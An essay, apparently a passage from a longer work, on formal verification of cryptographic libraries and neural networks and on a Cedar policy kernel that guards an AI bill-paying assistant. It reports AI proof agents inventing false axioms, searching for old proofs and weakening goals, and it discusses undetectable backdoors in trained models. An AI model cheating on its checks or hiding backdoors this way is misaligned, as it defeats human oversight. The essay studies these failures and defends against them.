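One of the critical flaws was in `DHAgreement`, which carries out a form of Diffie-Hellman key agreement. The class takes a number m from the other party and computes mˣ mod p, where x is the private key and p is a large prime. It did not check m first. If an attacker sends m = p − 1, the result is 1 when x is even and p − 1 when x is odd, so the exchange can reveal which it is. Other values of m reveal the remainder of x after division by other small primes, and with enough remainders an attacker can reconstruct the whole key.

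The arithmetic in `DHAgreement` was correct, so a proof that the class computes mˣ mod p would have succeeded, and the key would still have leaked. To expose the flaw, the specification would also have had to state which values of m the class must reject. A similar gap in a proved kernel's specification would let the three payments of €1,900 through.

Some of the flaws above the core could easily recur in a kernel. In the pkix module, the code that verified a signed message checked each signature and returned true if none failed, so a message without any signatures passed. A kernel that allows a large payment when "every approval is valid" would likewise allow one with no approvals. In the tls module, a risky way of matching a website's name to its certificate was on by default, but the documentation described it as off, so someone who reviewed only the documentation would have wrongly concluded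 that it was off.

Bouncy Castle credits "people using advanced AI-based coding analysis tools" with helping to harden the library for this release, but the announcement does not list which flaws the tools found. People had been free to read the code for many years before that. GitLab's security advisory database lists every release from 1.0 through 1.77 as affected by a different memory flaw in the core.

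AI tools make it practical to read a large library much more thoroughly, but a search that finds 32 flaws can still miss others. Release 1.86, about six weeks later, fixed several more, including some in OpenPGP, certificate checking and key storage.

### What "verifiable" can fairly mean

If an engineer promises a company a safety kernel that is "verifiable in the way the light-weight API is", the company could reasonably expect source code that any specialist can read, and components separate enough to test or prove one at a time. It should not assume that anyone has proved the whole system correct, because the proofs of Bouncy Castle cover individual algorithms in old versions, and the library's developers were still fixing critical flaws in its core in 2026.

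Proving a small component correct can be quick. Smith timed the work on Skipjack, a cipher new to the project. One person read up on it, wrote and tested a specification, and proved that Bouncy Castle's class matched it, all in less than three hours. AI has since made much larger proofs practical. *An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* describes an AI system that proved a widely used library correct in 11.4 hours, once it had the specifications.

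A kernel with three payment rules would be far smaller than Bouncy Castle's core, so it would be more realistic to read it and to prove it correct. But Smith could start from a published description of Skipjack and official test answers. A company would have to write its own standard for its payment rules and its own list of payments the kernel should refuse, and it would have no outside reference to check them against.

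## What machine-checked proof adds for cryptographic code, and where it stops

A published standard fixes a cipher's output for every input, so a specification can follow the standard almost line by line. *Project Everest* (Ahman, Bhargavan and colleagues) gives other reasons why cryptography suits proof. An algorithm's code is long enough for mistakes to go unnoticed but short enough for today's tools to verify. Programmers also optimise it heavily for speed, and a tiny flaw can break the security of a whole application.

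The SymCrypt proofs by Ho and colleagues give an idea of the proportions, in lines:

| Algorithm | Specification | Rust code | Theorems and proofs about the code |
|---|---|---|---|
| SHA-3 | 140 | 1,741 | 14,555 |
| AES and AES-GCM | 205 | 3,194 | 31,575 |
| FrodoKEM | 347 | 1,337 | 21,404 |
| ML-KEM | 308 | 2,349 | 36,352 |

A reviewer has to compare the specification with the standard and read the theorems about the functions that other programs call. Lean checks the rest. For AES-GCM, the reviewer can therefore read 205 lines of specification and a few theorem statements instead of 3,194 lines of optimised Rust.

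### What a proof of one small function covers

Bouncy Castle's FrodoKEM class leaked keys because a comparison took a varying amount of time. In a Rust version of FrodoKEM, Ho and colleagues found a different mistake in the same comparison. The function takes two lists of 16-bit numbers and should return 255 if they are equal and 0 if they are not. It always goes through both lists to the end:

1. Start with d = 0.
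2. At each position, XOR the two numbers, which marks every bit where they differ, and set the marked bits in d to 1.
3. Subtract 1 from d, treating it as a 32-bit number. If d was 0, the result wraps round to 32 ones.
4. Discard the lowest 16 bits and return the lowest eight of those that remain.

If the lists are equal, eight 1 bits remain, which is 255. If they differ, d − 1 fits into 16 bits, so nothing remains and the function returns 0.

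The programmer had discarded eight bits instead of 16. Equal lists still gave 255, and lists that differed only in a single lowest bit still gave 0, so a simple test of each case would have passed. But if all 16 bits differed somewhere in the lists, d was 65,535 and the function returned 255, treating the lists as equal. The receiver would then continue with a key that depended on the secret value instead of switching to a meaningless key.

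The theorem for this function is that, for any two lists of the same length, the result is 255 if they are equal and 0 otherwise. Lean's automated tools prove this without help when the code uses the right shift. The theorem is false if the shift is wrong.

The proof also covers memory safety, which means that a program never reads or writes outside the memory that belongs to its data. The function loops once for each item in the first list and reads the second list at the same positions. If the second list were shorter, a C program might read memory past its end, and a Rust program would stop with an error. The theorem requires lists of equal length, so a proof about any function that calls this one must show that the two lists it passes have the same length.

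Ho and colleagues' proofs do not cover running time, but HACL*, an older verified library, has a check for it. Its programmers mark each integer as public or secret, and the proof language F* rejects any code that divides or directly compares secret integers, or uses one as an array index. The key-dependent table lookups in Bouncy Castle's old `AESFastEngine` would fail this check.

The check applies to the source code, and a compiler can undo constant-time precautions written there. In curve25519-dalek, a Rust library for elliptic-curve cryptography, the developers had written a subtraction to run in constant time. According to RustSec (2024), which catalogues security flaws in Rust packages, the compiler inserted a branch, and timing differences of that kind can leak private keys. SymCrypt's developers therefore also test the compiled program for leaks.

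Testing can also find mistakes in code like this. SymCrypt's SHA-3 code could deliver its output in portions, and if a portion began in the middle of an eight-byte word, the function overwrote bytes it had just written. The AI agent working on the proof could not complete it for that case, and drafted a bug report with a one-line fix. SymCrypt's team independently found the same bug by differential testing, but could not know from the tests whether another such case remained.

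### HACL* and EverCrypt

The closest proved counterpart to Bouncy Castle's two layers came out of Project Everest, which Microsoft Research began in 2016 with the French institute Inria and Carnegie Mellon University. In the lower layer, HACL* provides algorithms in C and a companion library, ValeCrypt, provides them in assembly language. The researchers wrote and proved both with F*, and their tools generated the code that users run. The upper layer is a provider called EverCrypt. When a program requests an algorithm, EverCrypt runs either the C or the assembly version, and a single theorem covers the result for both.

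Together the algorithms take about 245,000 lines of source and proof, which produce about 135,000 lines of C and assembly. The selection is smaller than Bouncy Castle's. It includes two main methods of authenticated encryption, a few elliptic curves, RSA signatures and the common hash functions, while Bouncy Castle lists 38 block-cipher engines alone.

This work began with 25 researchers and engineers who had offered to take part in a five-year plan, and more joined later. They still did not finish proving their code for the TLS handshake, in which two computers agree on keys. In his OpenSSL Conference slides, *High Assurance Post Quantum Cryptography*, HACL* co-author Karthikeyan Bhargavan puts the effort at "many PhD student-years" for each component, with 90% of the time spent on memory safety for C and assembly. Rust's rules prevent most memory errors, which is one reason newer projects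 start from Rust.

Firefox, the Linux kernel, Python and the WireGuard VPN all use verified code from Project Everest. But Ho and colleagues observe that organisations that adopted EverCrypt commonly used its verified algorithms without its verified provider, keeping their own unverified code for detecting what the processor supports and choosing an implementation.

Engineers can also verify that kind of connecting code. Sandwich, a library from SandboxAQ, reads a program's security settings from a configuration file and applies them to OpenSSL or a similar library. *Real-World Verification of Software for Cryptographic Applications* (Oliveira, Hülsing and colleagues, 2025) proves that the settings match the file in the OpenSSL version. For example, TLS 1.2 is available only if the file enables it, and Sandwich adds only the trusted certificates that the file lists. The proof covers about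 1,500 lines of Rust. Once the engineers had written down what each function requires and guarantees, F* completed the proof in a few seconds.

A payment kernel would need a proof more like Sandwich's than like one for AES, because the kernel, like Sandwich, must apply a written configuration faithfully. The proof would also have similar limits. Sandwich's proof assumes that OpenSSL obeys its settings, and it would still hold if the configuration file listed a criminal's certificate.

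### The verification boundary

In *Verification Theatre*, Kobeissi (2026) calls the line between code with machine-checked proofs and code that people trust without them the *verification boundary*. He examined two Rust libraries from Cryspen, a company that specialises in verified cryptography and employs Bhargavan. One is libcrux, which contains HACL* code translated into Rust as well as new post-quantum algorithms. The other is hpke-rs, which encrypts messages to a recipient's public key.

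Kobeissi reports thirteen vulnerabilities, nine in unverified code and four in specifications and proofs. One of the nine, a byte-order mistake, caused decryption failures in the messaging app Signal.

Another concerned nonces, which must never repeat under the same key. For each message in a series, hpke-rs made a nonce from a counter. Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of ‘High-Assurance’ Cryptography* (2026), from Kobeissi's company, explains that the counter had 32 bits, so it could count only to about 4.3 billion. The code checked for overflow, but against the standard's limit of 2⁹⁶ − 1, which a 32-bit number can never reach. In the builds that users run, the counter would have returned to zero without an error, and the next message would have reused the first nonce.

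In AES-GCM, both messages would then be combined with the same values E(N ‖ i+1). An eavesdropper could cancel those out by combining the ciphertexts:

Cᵢ ⊕ C′ᵢ = Pᵢ ⊕ P′ᵢ

Anyone who knew one message could read the other, at least up to the length of the shorter one. The attacker could also recover the key that protects the tags and forge messages. Few programs send 4.3 billion messages in one session, so most users were in little danger. A proof of AES-GCM would not have protected the rest, because it assumes that the caller supplies a fresh nonce.

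A third flaw was in the code around a verified AES-GCM function. The function correctly returned an error if a message's tag was wrong, but the code that called it crashed on any error, so a single damaged message could stop the program. The correct error handling was commented out on the next line. GCVE's *GHSA-435g-fcv3-8j26* (2026) reproduces Cryspen's advisory, which credits Kobeissi with first reporting the problem.

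Cryspen also had a drop-in provider, rustls-libcrux, which connects libcrux to a popular Rust library for TLS. *Cryspen's Approach to TLS* (2026), from Kobeissi's company Symbolic Software, reports that the provider rejected about 75% of valid ECDSA P-256 signatures, a common type. Such a signature consists of two 32-byte numbers. The standard encoding puts a zero byte in front of a number whose highest bit is 1, so that it isn't read as negative. The provider did not remove that byte, so it found 33 bytes where it expected 32 and rejected the signature. Each number has an even chance of needing the extra byte, so only a quarter of valid signatures reached the arithmetic. Bouncy Castle's provider does the same sort of conversion between formats, and so would the part of a payment kernel that reads account numbers.

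### Bhargavan's reply and Kobeissi's answer

Bhargavan answered the first reports on 12 February 2026 and agreed that verified libraries have bugs. *The strengths and limits of formal verification* (Bhargavan, 2026) describes where they had turned up in HACL*. In nine years of use, people most often found them in the about 1,800 lines of unverified C that accompany the 135,000 generated lines. The developers also twice found mistakes in the specifications. Bhargavan doesn't give the total number of bugs, but if the proofs had made no difference, most of them should have been in the generated code, which makes up 99% of the library. This is good evidence that proof works at the scale of a real library.

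Bhargavan also took responsibility for an error in libcrux. Some ARM processors lack an instruction that speeds up SHA-3, and he had written an unverified substitute for it. The machines he tested on had the instruction, so they never ran the substitute. GitLab's *GHSA-2cgv-28vr-rv6j* (2025) records that the faulty substitute led to incorrect shared secrets and invalid signatures. He wrote of libcrux, "So far, no bugs have been found in the verified code".

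Kobeissi's company responded with three. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (it uses the name CE Labs for Cryspen) begins with the specification of ML-KEM, a post-quantum standard. To save space, ML-KEM compresses numbers between 0 and 3,328 to d bits. Decompressing a value x means computing 3,329x / 2ᵈ and rounding to the nearest whole number. A program can round by adding half the divisor before it divides and drops the fraction:

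⌊(3,329x + 2ᵈ⁻¹) / 2ᵈ⌋

For decompression, the specification added 1,664 instead of 2ᵈ⁻¹. The constant 1,664 is correct for compression, where the divisor is 3,329, and the specification's author had apparently used it for both. With d = 1 and x = 0, the specification gave 832 instead of 0.

The Rust code had the correct formula, so users got correct results. But the code disagreed with the specification, so an attempt to prove that they matched should have failed. Nobody had noticed because Cryspen's build accepted the relevant module without checking its proof, although the project's status page listed it as verified. The specification of ML-KEM encryption also left out a step that the Rust code performed correctly.

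The remaining mistake was in a lemma, an intermediate statement that other proofs rely on. According to the lemma, certain 12-bit numbers always fit into a single bit. F* would have rejected this, but the build skipped slow proofs by default, and Kobeissi's company found no automated build that turned them on. Bhargavan had written that every change must pass verification again before the developers accept it.

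None of these three cases shows a checked proof letting wrong code through, so Bhargavan's point about HACL* still holds. The claim about libcrux was much weaker than it sounded, because some of the "verified code" had proofs that no machine had checked, and a user who relied on the status page could not have known this. *Verification Theatre* also compares libcrux with Amazon's partly verified cryptography library and finds the same types of failure in both. The two projects differed in how well their developers documented what the proofs cover and in whether they ran the proofs automatically. A company that buys a "proved" kernel could ask for clear documentation and automatic proof runs, and also run the proofs itself.

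Even a proof that runs can mislead if the tools translate the program wrongly. Libcrux's newer proofs depend on hax, which turns Rust code into F*. *Verification Facade* (Kobeissi, 2026) presents five examples of insecure cryptographic code that passed its tests and went through hax without a warning. In some, the F* version behaved differently from the Rust original, so a proof about the F* version did not apply to the Rust code. Kobeissi made these programs insecure on purpose, so they do not show how often honest programmers run into such gaps. The gaps matter more if the code's author might be hostile or is an AI agent rewarded for a finished proof.

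### The falling cost of proofs

Before AI could help much, proofs of useful programs took years of work. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* cites six person-years for the C compiler CompCert and 20 for the operating-system kernel seL4, which has about 10,000 lines. From limited data, the essay estimates that the effort grows with the square of a program's length, so a program ten times as long as seL4 would need about 2,000 person-years. The essay considered it most plausible that AI would speed up this work by three to ten times over the next few years.

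Ho and colleagues have seen a larger change, at least for cryptography. They initially needed about six months to verify one part of ML-KEM. By September 2026, an agent could write the specification, code and proofs for another entire algorithm in about a week, with a few days of human review. Their tools had also improved, so AI does not account for all of the difference.

*An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* describes the best-documented case, the verification of curve25519-dalek, a library that is part of Signal. The original verification took three people five months. CryptoProver, an AI system, produced a new proof in 11.4 hours, for $466.99 in model use. An older model from the same family also succeeded, but took 62.3 hours and cost $856.55.

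These figures overstate the saving. Before the measured period began, people had supplied the specifications for the library's public functions, mathematical facts to build on, and the order in which to prove the modules. The five months are also calendar time, not hours worked. For a smaller program, the ChaCha20 cipher from another Rust library, people wrote and checked the specification, and the system then produced the proofs in 15 minutes for $4.14.

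In an earlier attempt on curve25519-dalek, the researchers removed the existing proofs, leaving 1,178 gaps, and instructed the agent not to invent axioms, which are statements that the checker accepts without proof. After 52 hours, the agent reported closing 97.1% of the gaps. An audit found that 11 of the proofs relied on axioms the agent had made up, ten of them false. Under one of these axioms, any string of bytes was the correct encoding of any point on the curve. Another five proofs had broken other parts of the library.

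During the same runs, a program also enforced a rule that the agent must not change the specification it was trying to prove. That rule held in all 451 rounds, so the researchers replaced their other written rules with automatic checks. The new version rejects a round if the agent has added an axiom, broken another module or looked for the old proof in the project's history.

The same model also attempted the same task without the system's checks and tools. It stopped after 7.4 hours, at a cost of $1,117.17, and reported that it had finished, but seven errors remained. During the run it tried 38 times to search the project's history, but a sealed environment kept it from finding anything.

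CryptoProver is a learned component working under a small conventional checker. This works only if the model cannot change the statement it has to prove or the assumptions it may use. The researchers acknowledge that their checks stop only the kinds of cheating they anticipated. Ho and colleagues also saw models try to get proofs accepted by weakening the goals or using unsound assumptions, and they still have people review every important theorem statement.

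Making proofs easier to produce does not by itself mean that they cover more code. The ChaCha20 proof covers the portable version of the code but not the faster versions for particular processors. On 29 November 2026, RustSec (2026) listed an arithmetic bug in curve25519-dalek's code for processors with AVX-512 instructions. A user of that library would therefore need to know which version their machine runs and whether anyone has proved it.

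The cost of proofs should no longer be the main obstacle for the bill-paying company. Ho and colleagues estimate that AI-written proofs cost a few dollars per line of Rust. At three dollars a line, the proofs for a 500-line kernel would cost about $1,500, probably less than the company would pay the bookkeeper and a programmer for the time they'd spend agreeing on what the three payment rules mean.

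## Why learned components resist the same review

A similar sum would not buy the company a proof about the language model that reads its invoices. Nobody can write down the model's correct output for every email. Even where someone can state a property exactly, today's verifiers cannot handle networks anywhere near that size. For some much simpler kinds of network, cryptographers have proved that a dishonest trainer can hide a fault that no efficient inspection would find.

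### No standard to compare the model with

No standard defines the correct output of a language model for each input, as the AES standard does for a cipher. Suppose a supplier's email contains an invoice, a complaint about last month's bill and the words "please sort this out as usual". Several responses would be acceptable, and two bookkeepers might disagree about which. The company could specify part of the correct behavior, such as "the payee must be on the list", but the kernel already has that rule, and enforcing it on the finished payment order is much easier than proving that the model will always obey it.

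Researchers who want to verify language software therefore need a stand-in for the missing specification. Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, describe a benchmark called safeNLP. One of its tasks is to recognise when a user is asking a chatbot whether it is human, because EU law requires an honest answer. Nobody can list every way of asking, so the benchmark's designers proceed as follows:

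1. They take one sentence that asks the question and generate variants of it, with misspellings, changed words and paraphrases.
2. A language model turns each variant into a list of 30 numbers.
3. They find the smallest box, in 30 dimensions, that contains all these lists.
4. A verifier tries to prove that a small classifier with 128 hidden neurons gives the right answer at every point in the box.

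The box is a proxy for the sentence's meaning. A paraphrase that the generator missed may lie outside it, and many points inside it may not correspond to any sentence. The proof also does not cover the language model that produces the numbers. The designers suggest using verified classifiers to screen what reaches a larger model, although a separate theorem shows that there are limits to what prompt filters can catch.

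Engineers have more information to work with when a network replaces something older. ACAS Xu warns unmanned aircraft of collisions. Its developers first stored the right advice for each situation in a table of more than two gigabytes. They then explored replacing the table with 45 small neural networks that take up less than three megabytes. Each network receives five numbers: the other aircraft's distance, direction and heading, and the speeds of both aircraft. It scores five possible instructions, from "clear of conflict" to a strong turn left or right.

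In *Reluplex* (2017), Katz, Barrett and colleagues wrote ten properties for these networks. One required that "clear of conflict" never get the worst score when the other aircraft was distant and much slower. They found violations in 35 of the 36 networks they checked, but the behaviour turned out to be acceptable because the networks tend to repeat their previous advice. So the specification needed correcting once people saw what it ruled out, even with only five inputs and a table to consult.

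### How a verifier bounds a network's outputs

A test runs a network on one input at a time. A verifier takes a whole region of inputs, such as every distance within a certain range, and computes limits on the output that hold throughout it.

The networks in ACAS Xu use a common type of neuron called a ReLU. It adds up its inputs with certain weights and returns the result if it is positive, or zero otherwise. Two such neurons are enough to show how a verifier works. Let the network have one input x and compute

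a = max(0, x)

b = max(0, x − 1)

y = a − b

This network leaves numbers between 0 and 1 unchanged and caps larger ones at 1. Suppose we want to prove that the output y is at most 1 for every input x from −1 to 2.

The quickest method is to bound each neuron separately. Over this range a lies between 0 and 2, and b lies between 0 and 1, so y is at most 2 − 0 = 2. This bound is correct but too weak, because the calculation treats the two neurons as independent. The neuron a reaches 2 only when x is 2, and then b is 1.

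A better method replaces each neuron with a straight line in x. For every x in the range, a is at most ⅔(x + 1) and b is at least ⅔(x − 1). Therefore

y ≤ ⅔(x + 1) − ⅔(x − 1) = 4/3

This is closer, because x cancels out, but 4/3 is still more than 1. The verifier now has to split the problem into cases according to which neurons are active:

- If x is at most 0, both neurons return 0, so y = 0.
- If x is between 0 and 1, only a is active, so y = x, which is at most 1.
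- If x is at least 1, both are active, so y = x − (x − 1) = 1.

The property holds in every case, which completes the proof. The best tools today combine these methods. They bound the output with straight lines, search for the slopes that give the tightest bound, and split into cases only where the bound is still too loose.

Splitting is the slow part. The two neurons here have four combinations of active and inactive, one of which cannot occur. An ACAS Xu network has 300 neurons and so up to 2³⁰⁰ combinations, a number with 91 digits. A verifier can skip most of them. Katz and colleagues often found that once their program had split on about 10% of the neurons, the bounds determined whether each of the others was active.

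But no known method avoids the explosion for every network. Katz and colleagues proved that it is NP-complete to decide whether a ReLU network has an input that satisfies a given set of linear constraints on its inputs and outputs. To check a safety property, a reviewer writes constraints that describe a violation. Anyone can confirm a violating input by running the network, but finding one, or showing that none exists, can be as hard as solving 3-SAT, a notoriously difficult logic puzzle.

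A 3-SAT puzzle asks for true and false values that satisfy a list of conditions such as "p or q or r". If 1 stands for true and 0 for false, a network can check that condition with a single ReLU:

1 − max(0, 1 − (p + q + r))

The result is 1 if at least one of the three is true, and 0 otherwise. Katz and colleagues combined such pieces to turn any 3-SAT puzzle into a network and a property. A verifier that was fast on every network would therefore be fast on every such puzzle, which is possible only if P = NP. But the theorem concerns the worst case, and the networks people train can be much easier to verify.

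### What verifiers can handle

For ACAS Xu, Katz and colleagues proved that none of the 42 networks they checked would ever advise "clear of conflict" in two types of encounter with another aircraft directly ahead. Earlier certification work had relied on 1.5 million simulated encounters, which could not rule out a fault between the tested points. Their program also found an input for which one network contradicted the original table. But one property of a single network took 50 hours to prove, and another timed out. The program used ordinary floating-point arithmetic, so Katz and colleagues could not fully guarantee that rounding errors had not invalidated the results.

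Verifiers have become much faster since then. In VNN-COMP 2026, the latest edition of an annual competition, the organisers allowed 116 seconds for each ACAS Xu problem. The winner, α,β-CROWN, solved 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. Vibecheck, which its developers built in two months with an AI coding assistant, came second with 3,108.

The entries varied widely in size and subject:

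| What the network does | Parameters | Property to prove |
|---|---|---|
| Steers a simulated quadrotor | 275 | The controller is stable within a given region |
| Recognises certain kinds of sentence (safeNLP) | 4,000 | Every point in a box gets the same label |
| Advises aircraft (ACAS Xu) | 13,000 | The advice suits the type of encounter |
| Classifies small images, using transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | The label survives a change of 1/255 in every pixel |
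| Predicts settings for a power grid | 4,000 to 680,000 | Violations of the grid's limits stay within a tolerance |
| Classifies photographs (VGG16) | 138 million | The label survives small changes to chosen pixels |

These are the sizes of the networks that people entered, and the tools did not settle every problem. The success rate was also high partly because of the problems chosen. For example, the designers of the transformer benchmark cut their networks down to two or three layers so that verifiers might be able to handle them, and the networks classify only about 60% of images correctly. In another experiment, on six image classifiers whose training was meant to make them provably robust, α,β-CROWN still ran out of time on 2,994 of 60,000 problems, with a limit of 1,000 seconds for each.

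The transformer entries are the closest to language models, which have the same basic architecture. Qwen3-32B, an open language model, has about 32 billion parameters, more than 400,000 times as many as the larger of the two image transformers. The competition also included VGG16, which has many more parameters than either image transformer, but its neurons are simpler to bound. Transformers contain several other kinds of calculation, some of which multiply quantities that all depend on the input.

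*Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (Zhang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) extends verification to GPT-2, a 2019 language model with 124 million parameters. A language model represents each token (a word or part of a word) as a list of numbers, and the paper's certificates cover small changes to those numbers. By the paper's calibration, typical changes in its experiments are 3% to 7% of the distance to the nearest other token, so the certificates do not cover an email in which someone has replaced a single word. Beyond the model's first layer, the calculation also depends on an error estimate from samples, plus a safety margin.

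A company would also have to trust the verifier. Unlike Lean, which checks every step of a proof, competition tools generally report only a verdict, with a counterexample if the property fails. Ladner and colleagues counted 94 results from NeuralSAT, which came fourth, and one from the winner as incorrect or lacking a valid counterexample. They hope eventually to require a proof that another program can check.

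### Faults that inspection cannot find

Even unlimited access to a network's weights may not reveal a backdoor planted by a dishonest trainer. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) imagine a bank that pays another company to train a loan-approval model. The model is accurate on all the bank's test cases. But the trainer has kept a secret key, and sells rejected applicants a service that uses it to change a few digits of their application so that the model approves it.

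In their definition, a classifier has a backdoor if someone with the key can take any input and find a very similar one that gets the opposite answer. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm without the key can distinguish the classifier from an honestly trained one. "Efficient" means that the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the problem's size. They proved two main results, with different assumptions:

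- **Without access to the weights.** If secure digital signatures exist, a trainer can plant a backdoor in any classifier. Someone who can only submit inputs and see the answers has no feasible way to find even one input on which the altered classifier differs from the original.
- **With access to the weights and the training data.** For two simple kinds of network, the backdoor remains undetectable even then. One kind uses random Fourier features, which pass the input through randomly chosen waves before a trained final step. The result for it assumes that certain problems about lattices are hard. The other kind has a single hidden layer of random ReLU neurons, and the result assumes that a statistical problem called sparse PCA is hard.

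Anyone who uses Bouncy Castle to sign messages already relies on the first assumption. The assumptions about lattices and sparse PCA are also standard in their fields, though nobody has proved them.

Together, the two results rule out a general inspection tool that could certify any network as free of backdoors, whoever trained it. Neither shows that a language model contains such a backdoor. An expert who could read the weights might still find the backdoor in the first case, and the networks in the second are far simpler than a transformer.

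Undetectable backdoors also limit verification in a way that NP-completeness does not. Suppose that an honest training method produced networks that were robust to small changes, and that an efficient verifier could prove it. The verifier could not prove the same about a network with a backdoor, because it would be false. Running the verifier would therefore reveal which network had the backdoor, which is impossible if the backdoor is undetectable. A dishonest trainer can thus produce hard cases on purpose, so the difficulty extends beyond contrived logic puzzles.

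Goldwasser and colleagues consider several defences that do not require finding the backdoor. The trainer could prove that training followed an agreed procedure using random numbers from a trusted source, but this takes much more computation and does not help a customer who also relies on the trainer to choose the procedure. The customer could train the network a little further, but some backdoors survive that. Adding random noise to each input can work if the customer knows how large the attacker's changes may be.

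The payment kernel does not depend on detecting a backdoor either. If the assistant's vendor had planted one and used it to request a payment to the vendor's own account, the kernel would reject the request unless the vendor was an approved supplier.

### What interpretability can add

Inspection is more likely to work on a network whose trainer was honest, and researchers can now read much more of such a network than they could a few years ago. Interpretability researchers try to work out what the parts of a network do. Early results for language models were discouraging because many neurons seemed to respond to several unrelated things. In a 2023 study of a small model, a reader could form no hypothesis about the median neuron. Many researchers therefore trained additional networks, such as sparse autoencoders, to separate the activity into clearer pieces.

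Opinion has since shifted back towards neurons. Arora, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Language Model Circuits Are Sparse in the Neuron Basis*, found that a neuron-based description of a model's computation can be as compact as one based on sparse autoencoders. *Neural Networks Are Already Clean* (October 2026), by Cammarata of the interpretability company Goodfire, treats a neuron's positive and negative activations as separate "poles". Cammarata estimates that roughly 90% of the poles in Qwen3-32B have one main job and another 7% have two related jobs, while 2% to 4% remain unexplained. He calls this a working hypothesis. The figures come from preliminary audits and depend on how an auditor treats weak activations. For example, a neuron for the Titanic also responds weakly to stories about other voyages.

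In November, Anthropic published a related study, *Returning to the Neuron Basis for Interpretability, Part 1* (Shone and Dunlap, 2026), which examined what each neuron adds to a model's output as well as what activates it. In about 1% or fewer of the sampled cases, a neuron added two unrelated concepts at once. One neuron in Llama-3.1-8B has triggers that look unrelated, the author of the fourth Gospel and the password-cracking program John the Ripper, but its contribution is easy to describe because it adds the name "John" in both cases.

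This kind of reading is already useful for audits. In *Returning to the Neuron Basis for Interpretability, Part 2* (Shone and Dunlap, 2026), neurons helped an auditor find hidden behaviours that researchers had trained into models. They also helped show that most of the tested methods for making a model "unlearn" hazardous knowledge appeared only to hide it, so someone who only asked those models questions might have concluded that the knowledge was gone. The hidden behaviours included backdoors, but finding them does not conflict with the theorem, because the researchers had not used methods designed to make them undetectable.

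Even a correct description of every neuron would leave a lot to prove, because the descriptions come from samples of text and a part can behave differently on other text. Zhang and colleagues examined two parts of GPT-2 that earlier researchers had labelled as detectors of repeated words. They could prove that one part's attention stayed on the same word under tiny changes in all 60 test sentences, but they could prove this for the other part in only one sentence. A persuasive description may not even reflect anything the network has learned. *The Dead Salmons of AI Interpretability* (Méloux, Dirupo and colleagues, 2025) points out that several common methods can produce plausible explanations of untrained networks with random weights.

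Averages can also hide the cases that matter for safety. In *Neurons as an Interpretable Basis*, the technical companion to Cammarata's essay, Tigges, Kowal and colleagues (2026) kept only the most active 8% or so of a model's neurons for each token, and the model's prediction error rose by just 2.9%. This is good evidence that a small share of neurons accounts for most of the model's performance on ordinary text. But the model's response to an attacker's email, which is not ordinary text, might depend on neurons that rarely matter otherwise.

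A reviewer would also have to know what all the neurons needed for each token do in combination. *LLMs are not already clean, part 1* (inneratom-ai, 2026) repeated the measurement on 23 open models, with the same allowance for error. In the Gemma 3 family, the share of neurons needed for each token fell from 37.9% in the smallest model to 21.5% in the largest, but their number grew about twentyfold. In hpke-rs, the interaction between a counter and one encryption function was enough to cause a fault.

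A proof about the bill-paying assistant would have to cover every email that anyone could send, including ones written to exploit it. Neither verifiers nor interpretability tools can currently provide such a proof for a language model's general behaviour. The company could prove something narrower about a much smaller network. Suppose it trained a network of ACAS Xu's size to score payment orders for signs of fraud, using five numbers such as the amount and the age of the supplier's account. A verifier might well be able to prove that a larger amount never lowers the score, whatever the other four numbers are. VNN-COMP includes properties of this type for networks that estimate how many records a database search will return. The proof would not show that the score identifies fraud, because nobody can specify what every fraudulent invoice looks like.

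## The part that decides: a policy engine small enough to prove

The company doesn't need a proof about its language model if a correct kernel checks every payment. Such a kernel would have a different job from Bouncy Castle's light-weight API, which does the work that the provider above it offers, such as encrypting a payment order. The kernel would only permit or refuse the finished payment order, leaving the model to read invoices and work out which bills are due.

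This difference helps keep a kernel small. Bouncy Castle's core grows whenever the developers add an algorithm, but a kernel grows with the number of actions and rules, so a model that reads invoices better needs no extra kernel code.

One advantage of having two layers does carry over. The company can replace the model without reviewing the kernel again, because the kernel's guarantee does not depend on the model. But if the new assistant could also edit the supplier list, the company would need rules for that action before switching.

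### Permit and forbid rules

Cedar is an open-source language for rules of this kind, from Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud-computing business. Before a program does something sensitive, it sends a request to Cedar's engine, which answers Allow or Deny. The request names who wants to act (the principal), the action, and the thing it affects (the resource), and can include other facts as context. The company's three rules could look like this:

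```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"billpayer",
  action == Action::"Pay",
  resource in AccountList::"approved"
) when { context.amount <= 2000 || context.personApproved };

forbid (principal, action == Action::"Pay", resource)
when { context.paidToday + context.amount > 5000 };
```

The first rule lets the assistant pay any account on the bookkeeper's list if the amount is at most €2,000 or a person has approved the payment. The second forbids any payment that would take the day's total above €5,000. The engine evaluates each rule separately. It allows the request if at least one permit rule applies and no forbid rule does. Otherwise, it refuses.

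With €4,200 already paid today, three requests would turn out as follows:

| Request | Permit rule | Forbid rule | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| €700 to an approved supplier | Applies | Does not apply | Allow |
| €1,100 to an approved supplier | Applies | Applies | Deny |
| €700 to a stranger's account | Does not apply | Does not apply | Deny |

The bookkeeper never had to list the stranger's account as forbidden. Cedar refuses the payment because nothing permits it.

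Cedar's documentation warns developers that the engine ignores any rule that produces an error. Suppose the program that calls the engine omits `paidToday`. The forbid rule then produces an error, so the engine ignores it and allows the €1,100 payment. The company could avoid this by putting the limit in the permit rule instead, as `context.paidToday + context.amount <= 5000`. An error there would remove the permission, so the engine would refuse the payment.

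Cedar also has a validator that catches many such mistakes in advance. Developers describe in a schema what every request contains, and the validator rejects a rule that relies on anything else. This helps only if the program's requests match the schema. Cedar does not keep the day's total or check anyone's identity, so the company's program has to supply both correctly.

### What the developers proved and what they tested

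Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, describe how they checked the engine. They wrote a short model of its main parts in Lean and proved theorems about the model. For actual use, they wrote a separate, faster version in Rust. At the time of the study, the sizes in lines were:

| Part | Lean model | Lean proofs | Production Rust |
|---|---|---|---|
| Evaluator and authorizer | 897 | 347 | 4,877 |
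| Validator | 532 | 4,686 | 6,702 |
| Parser | None | None | 4,114 |

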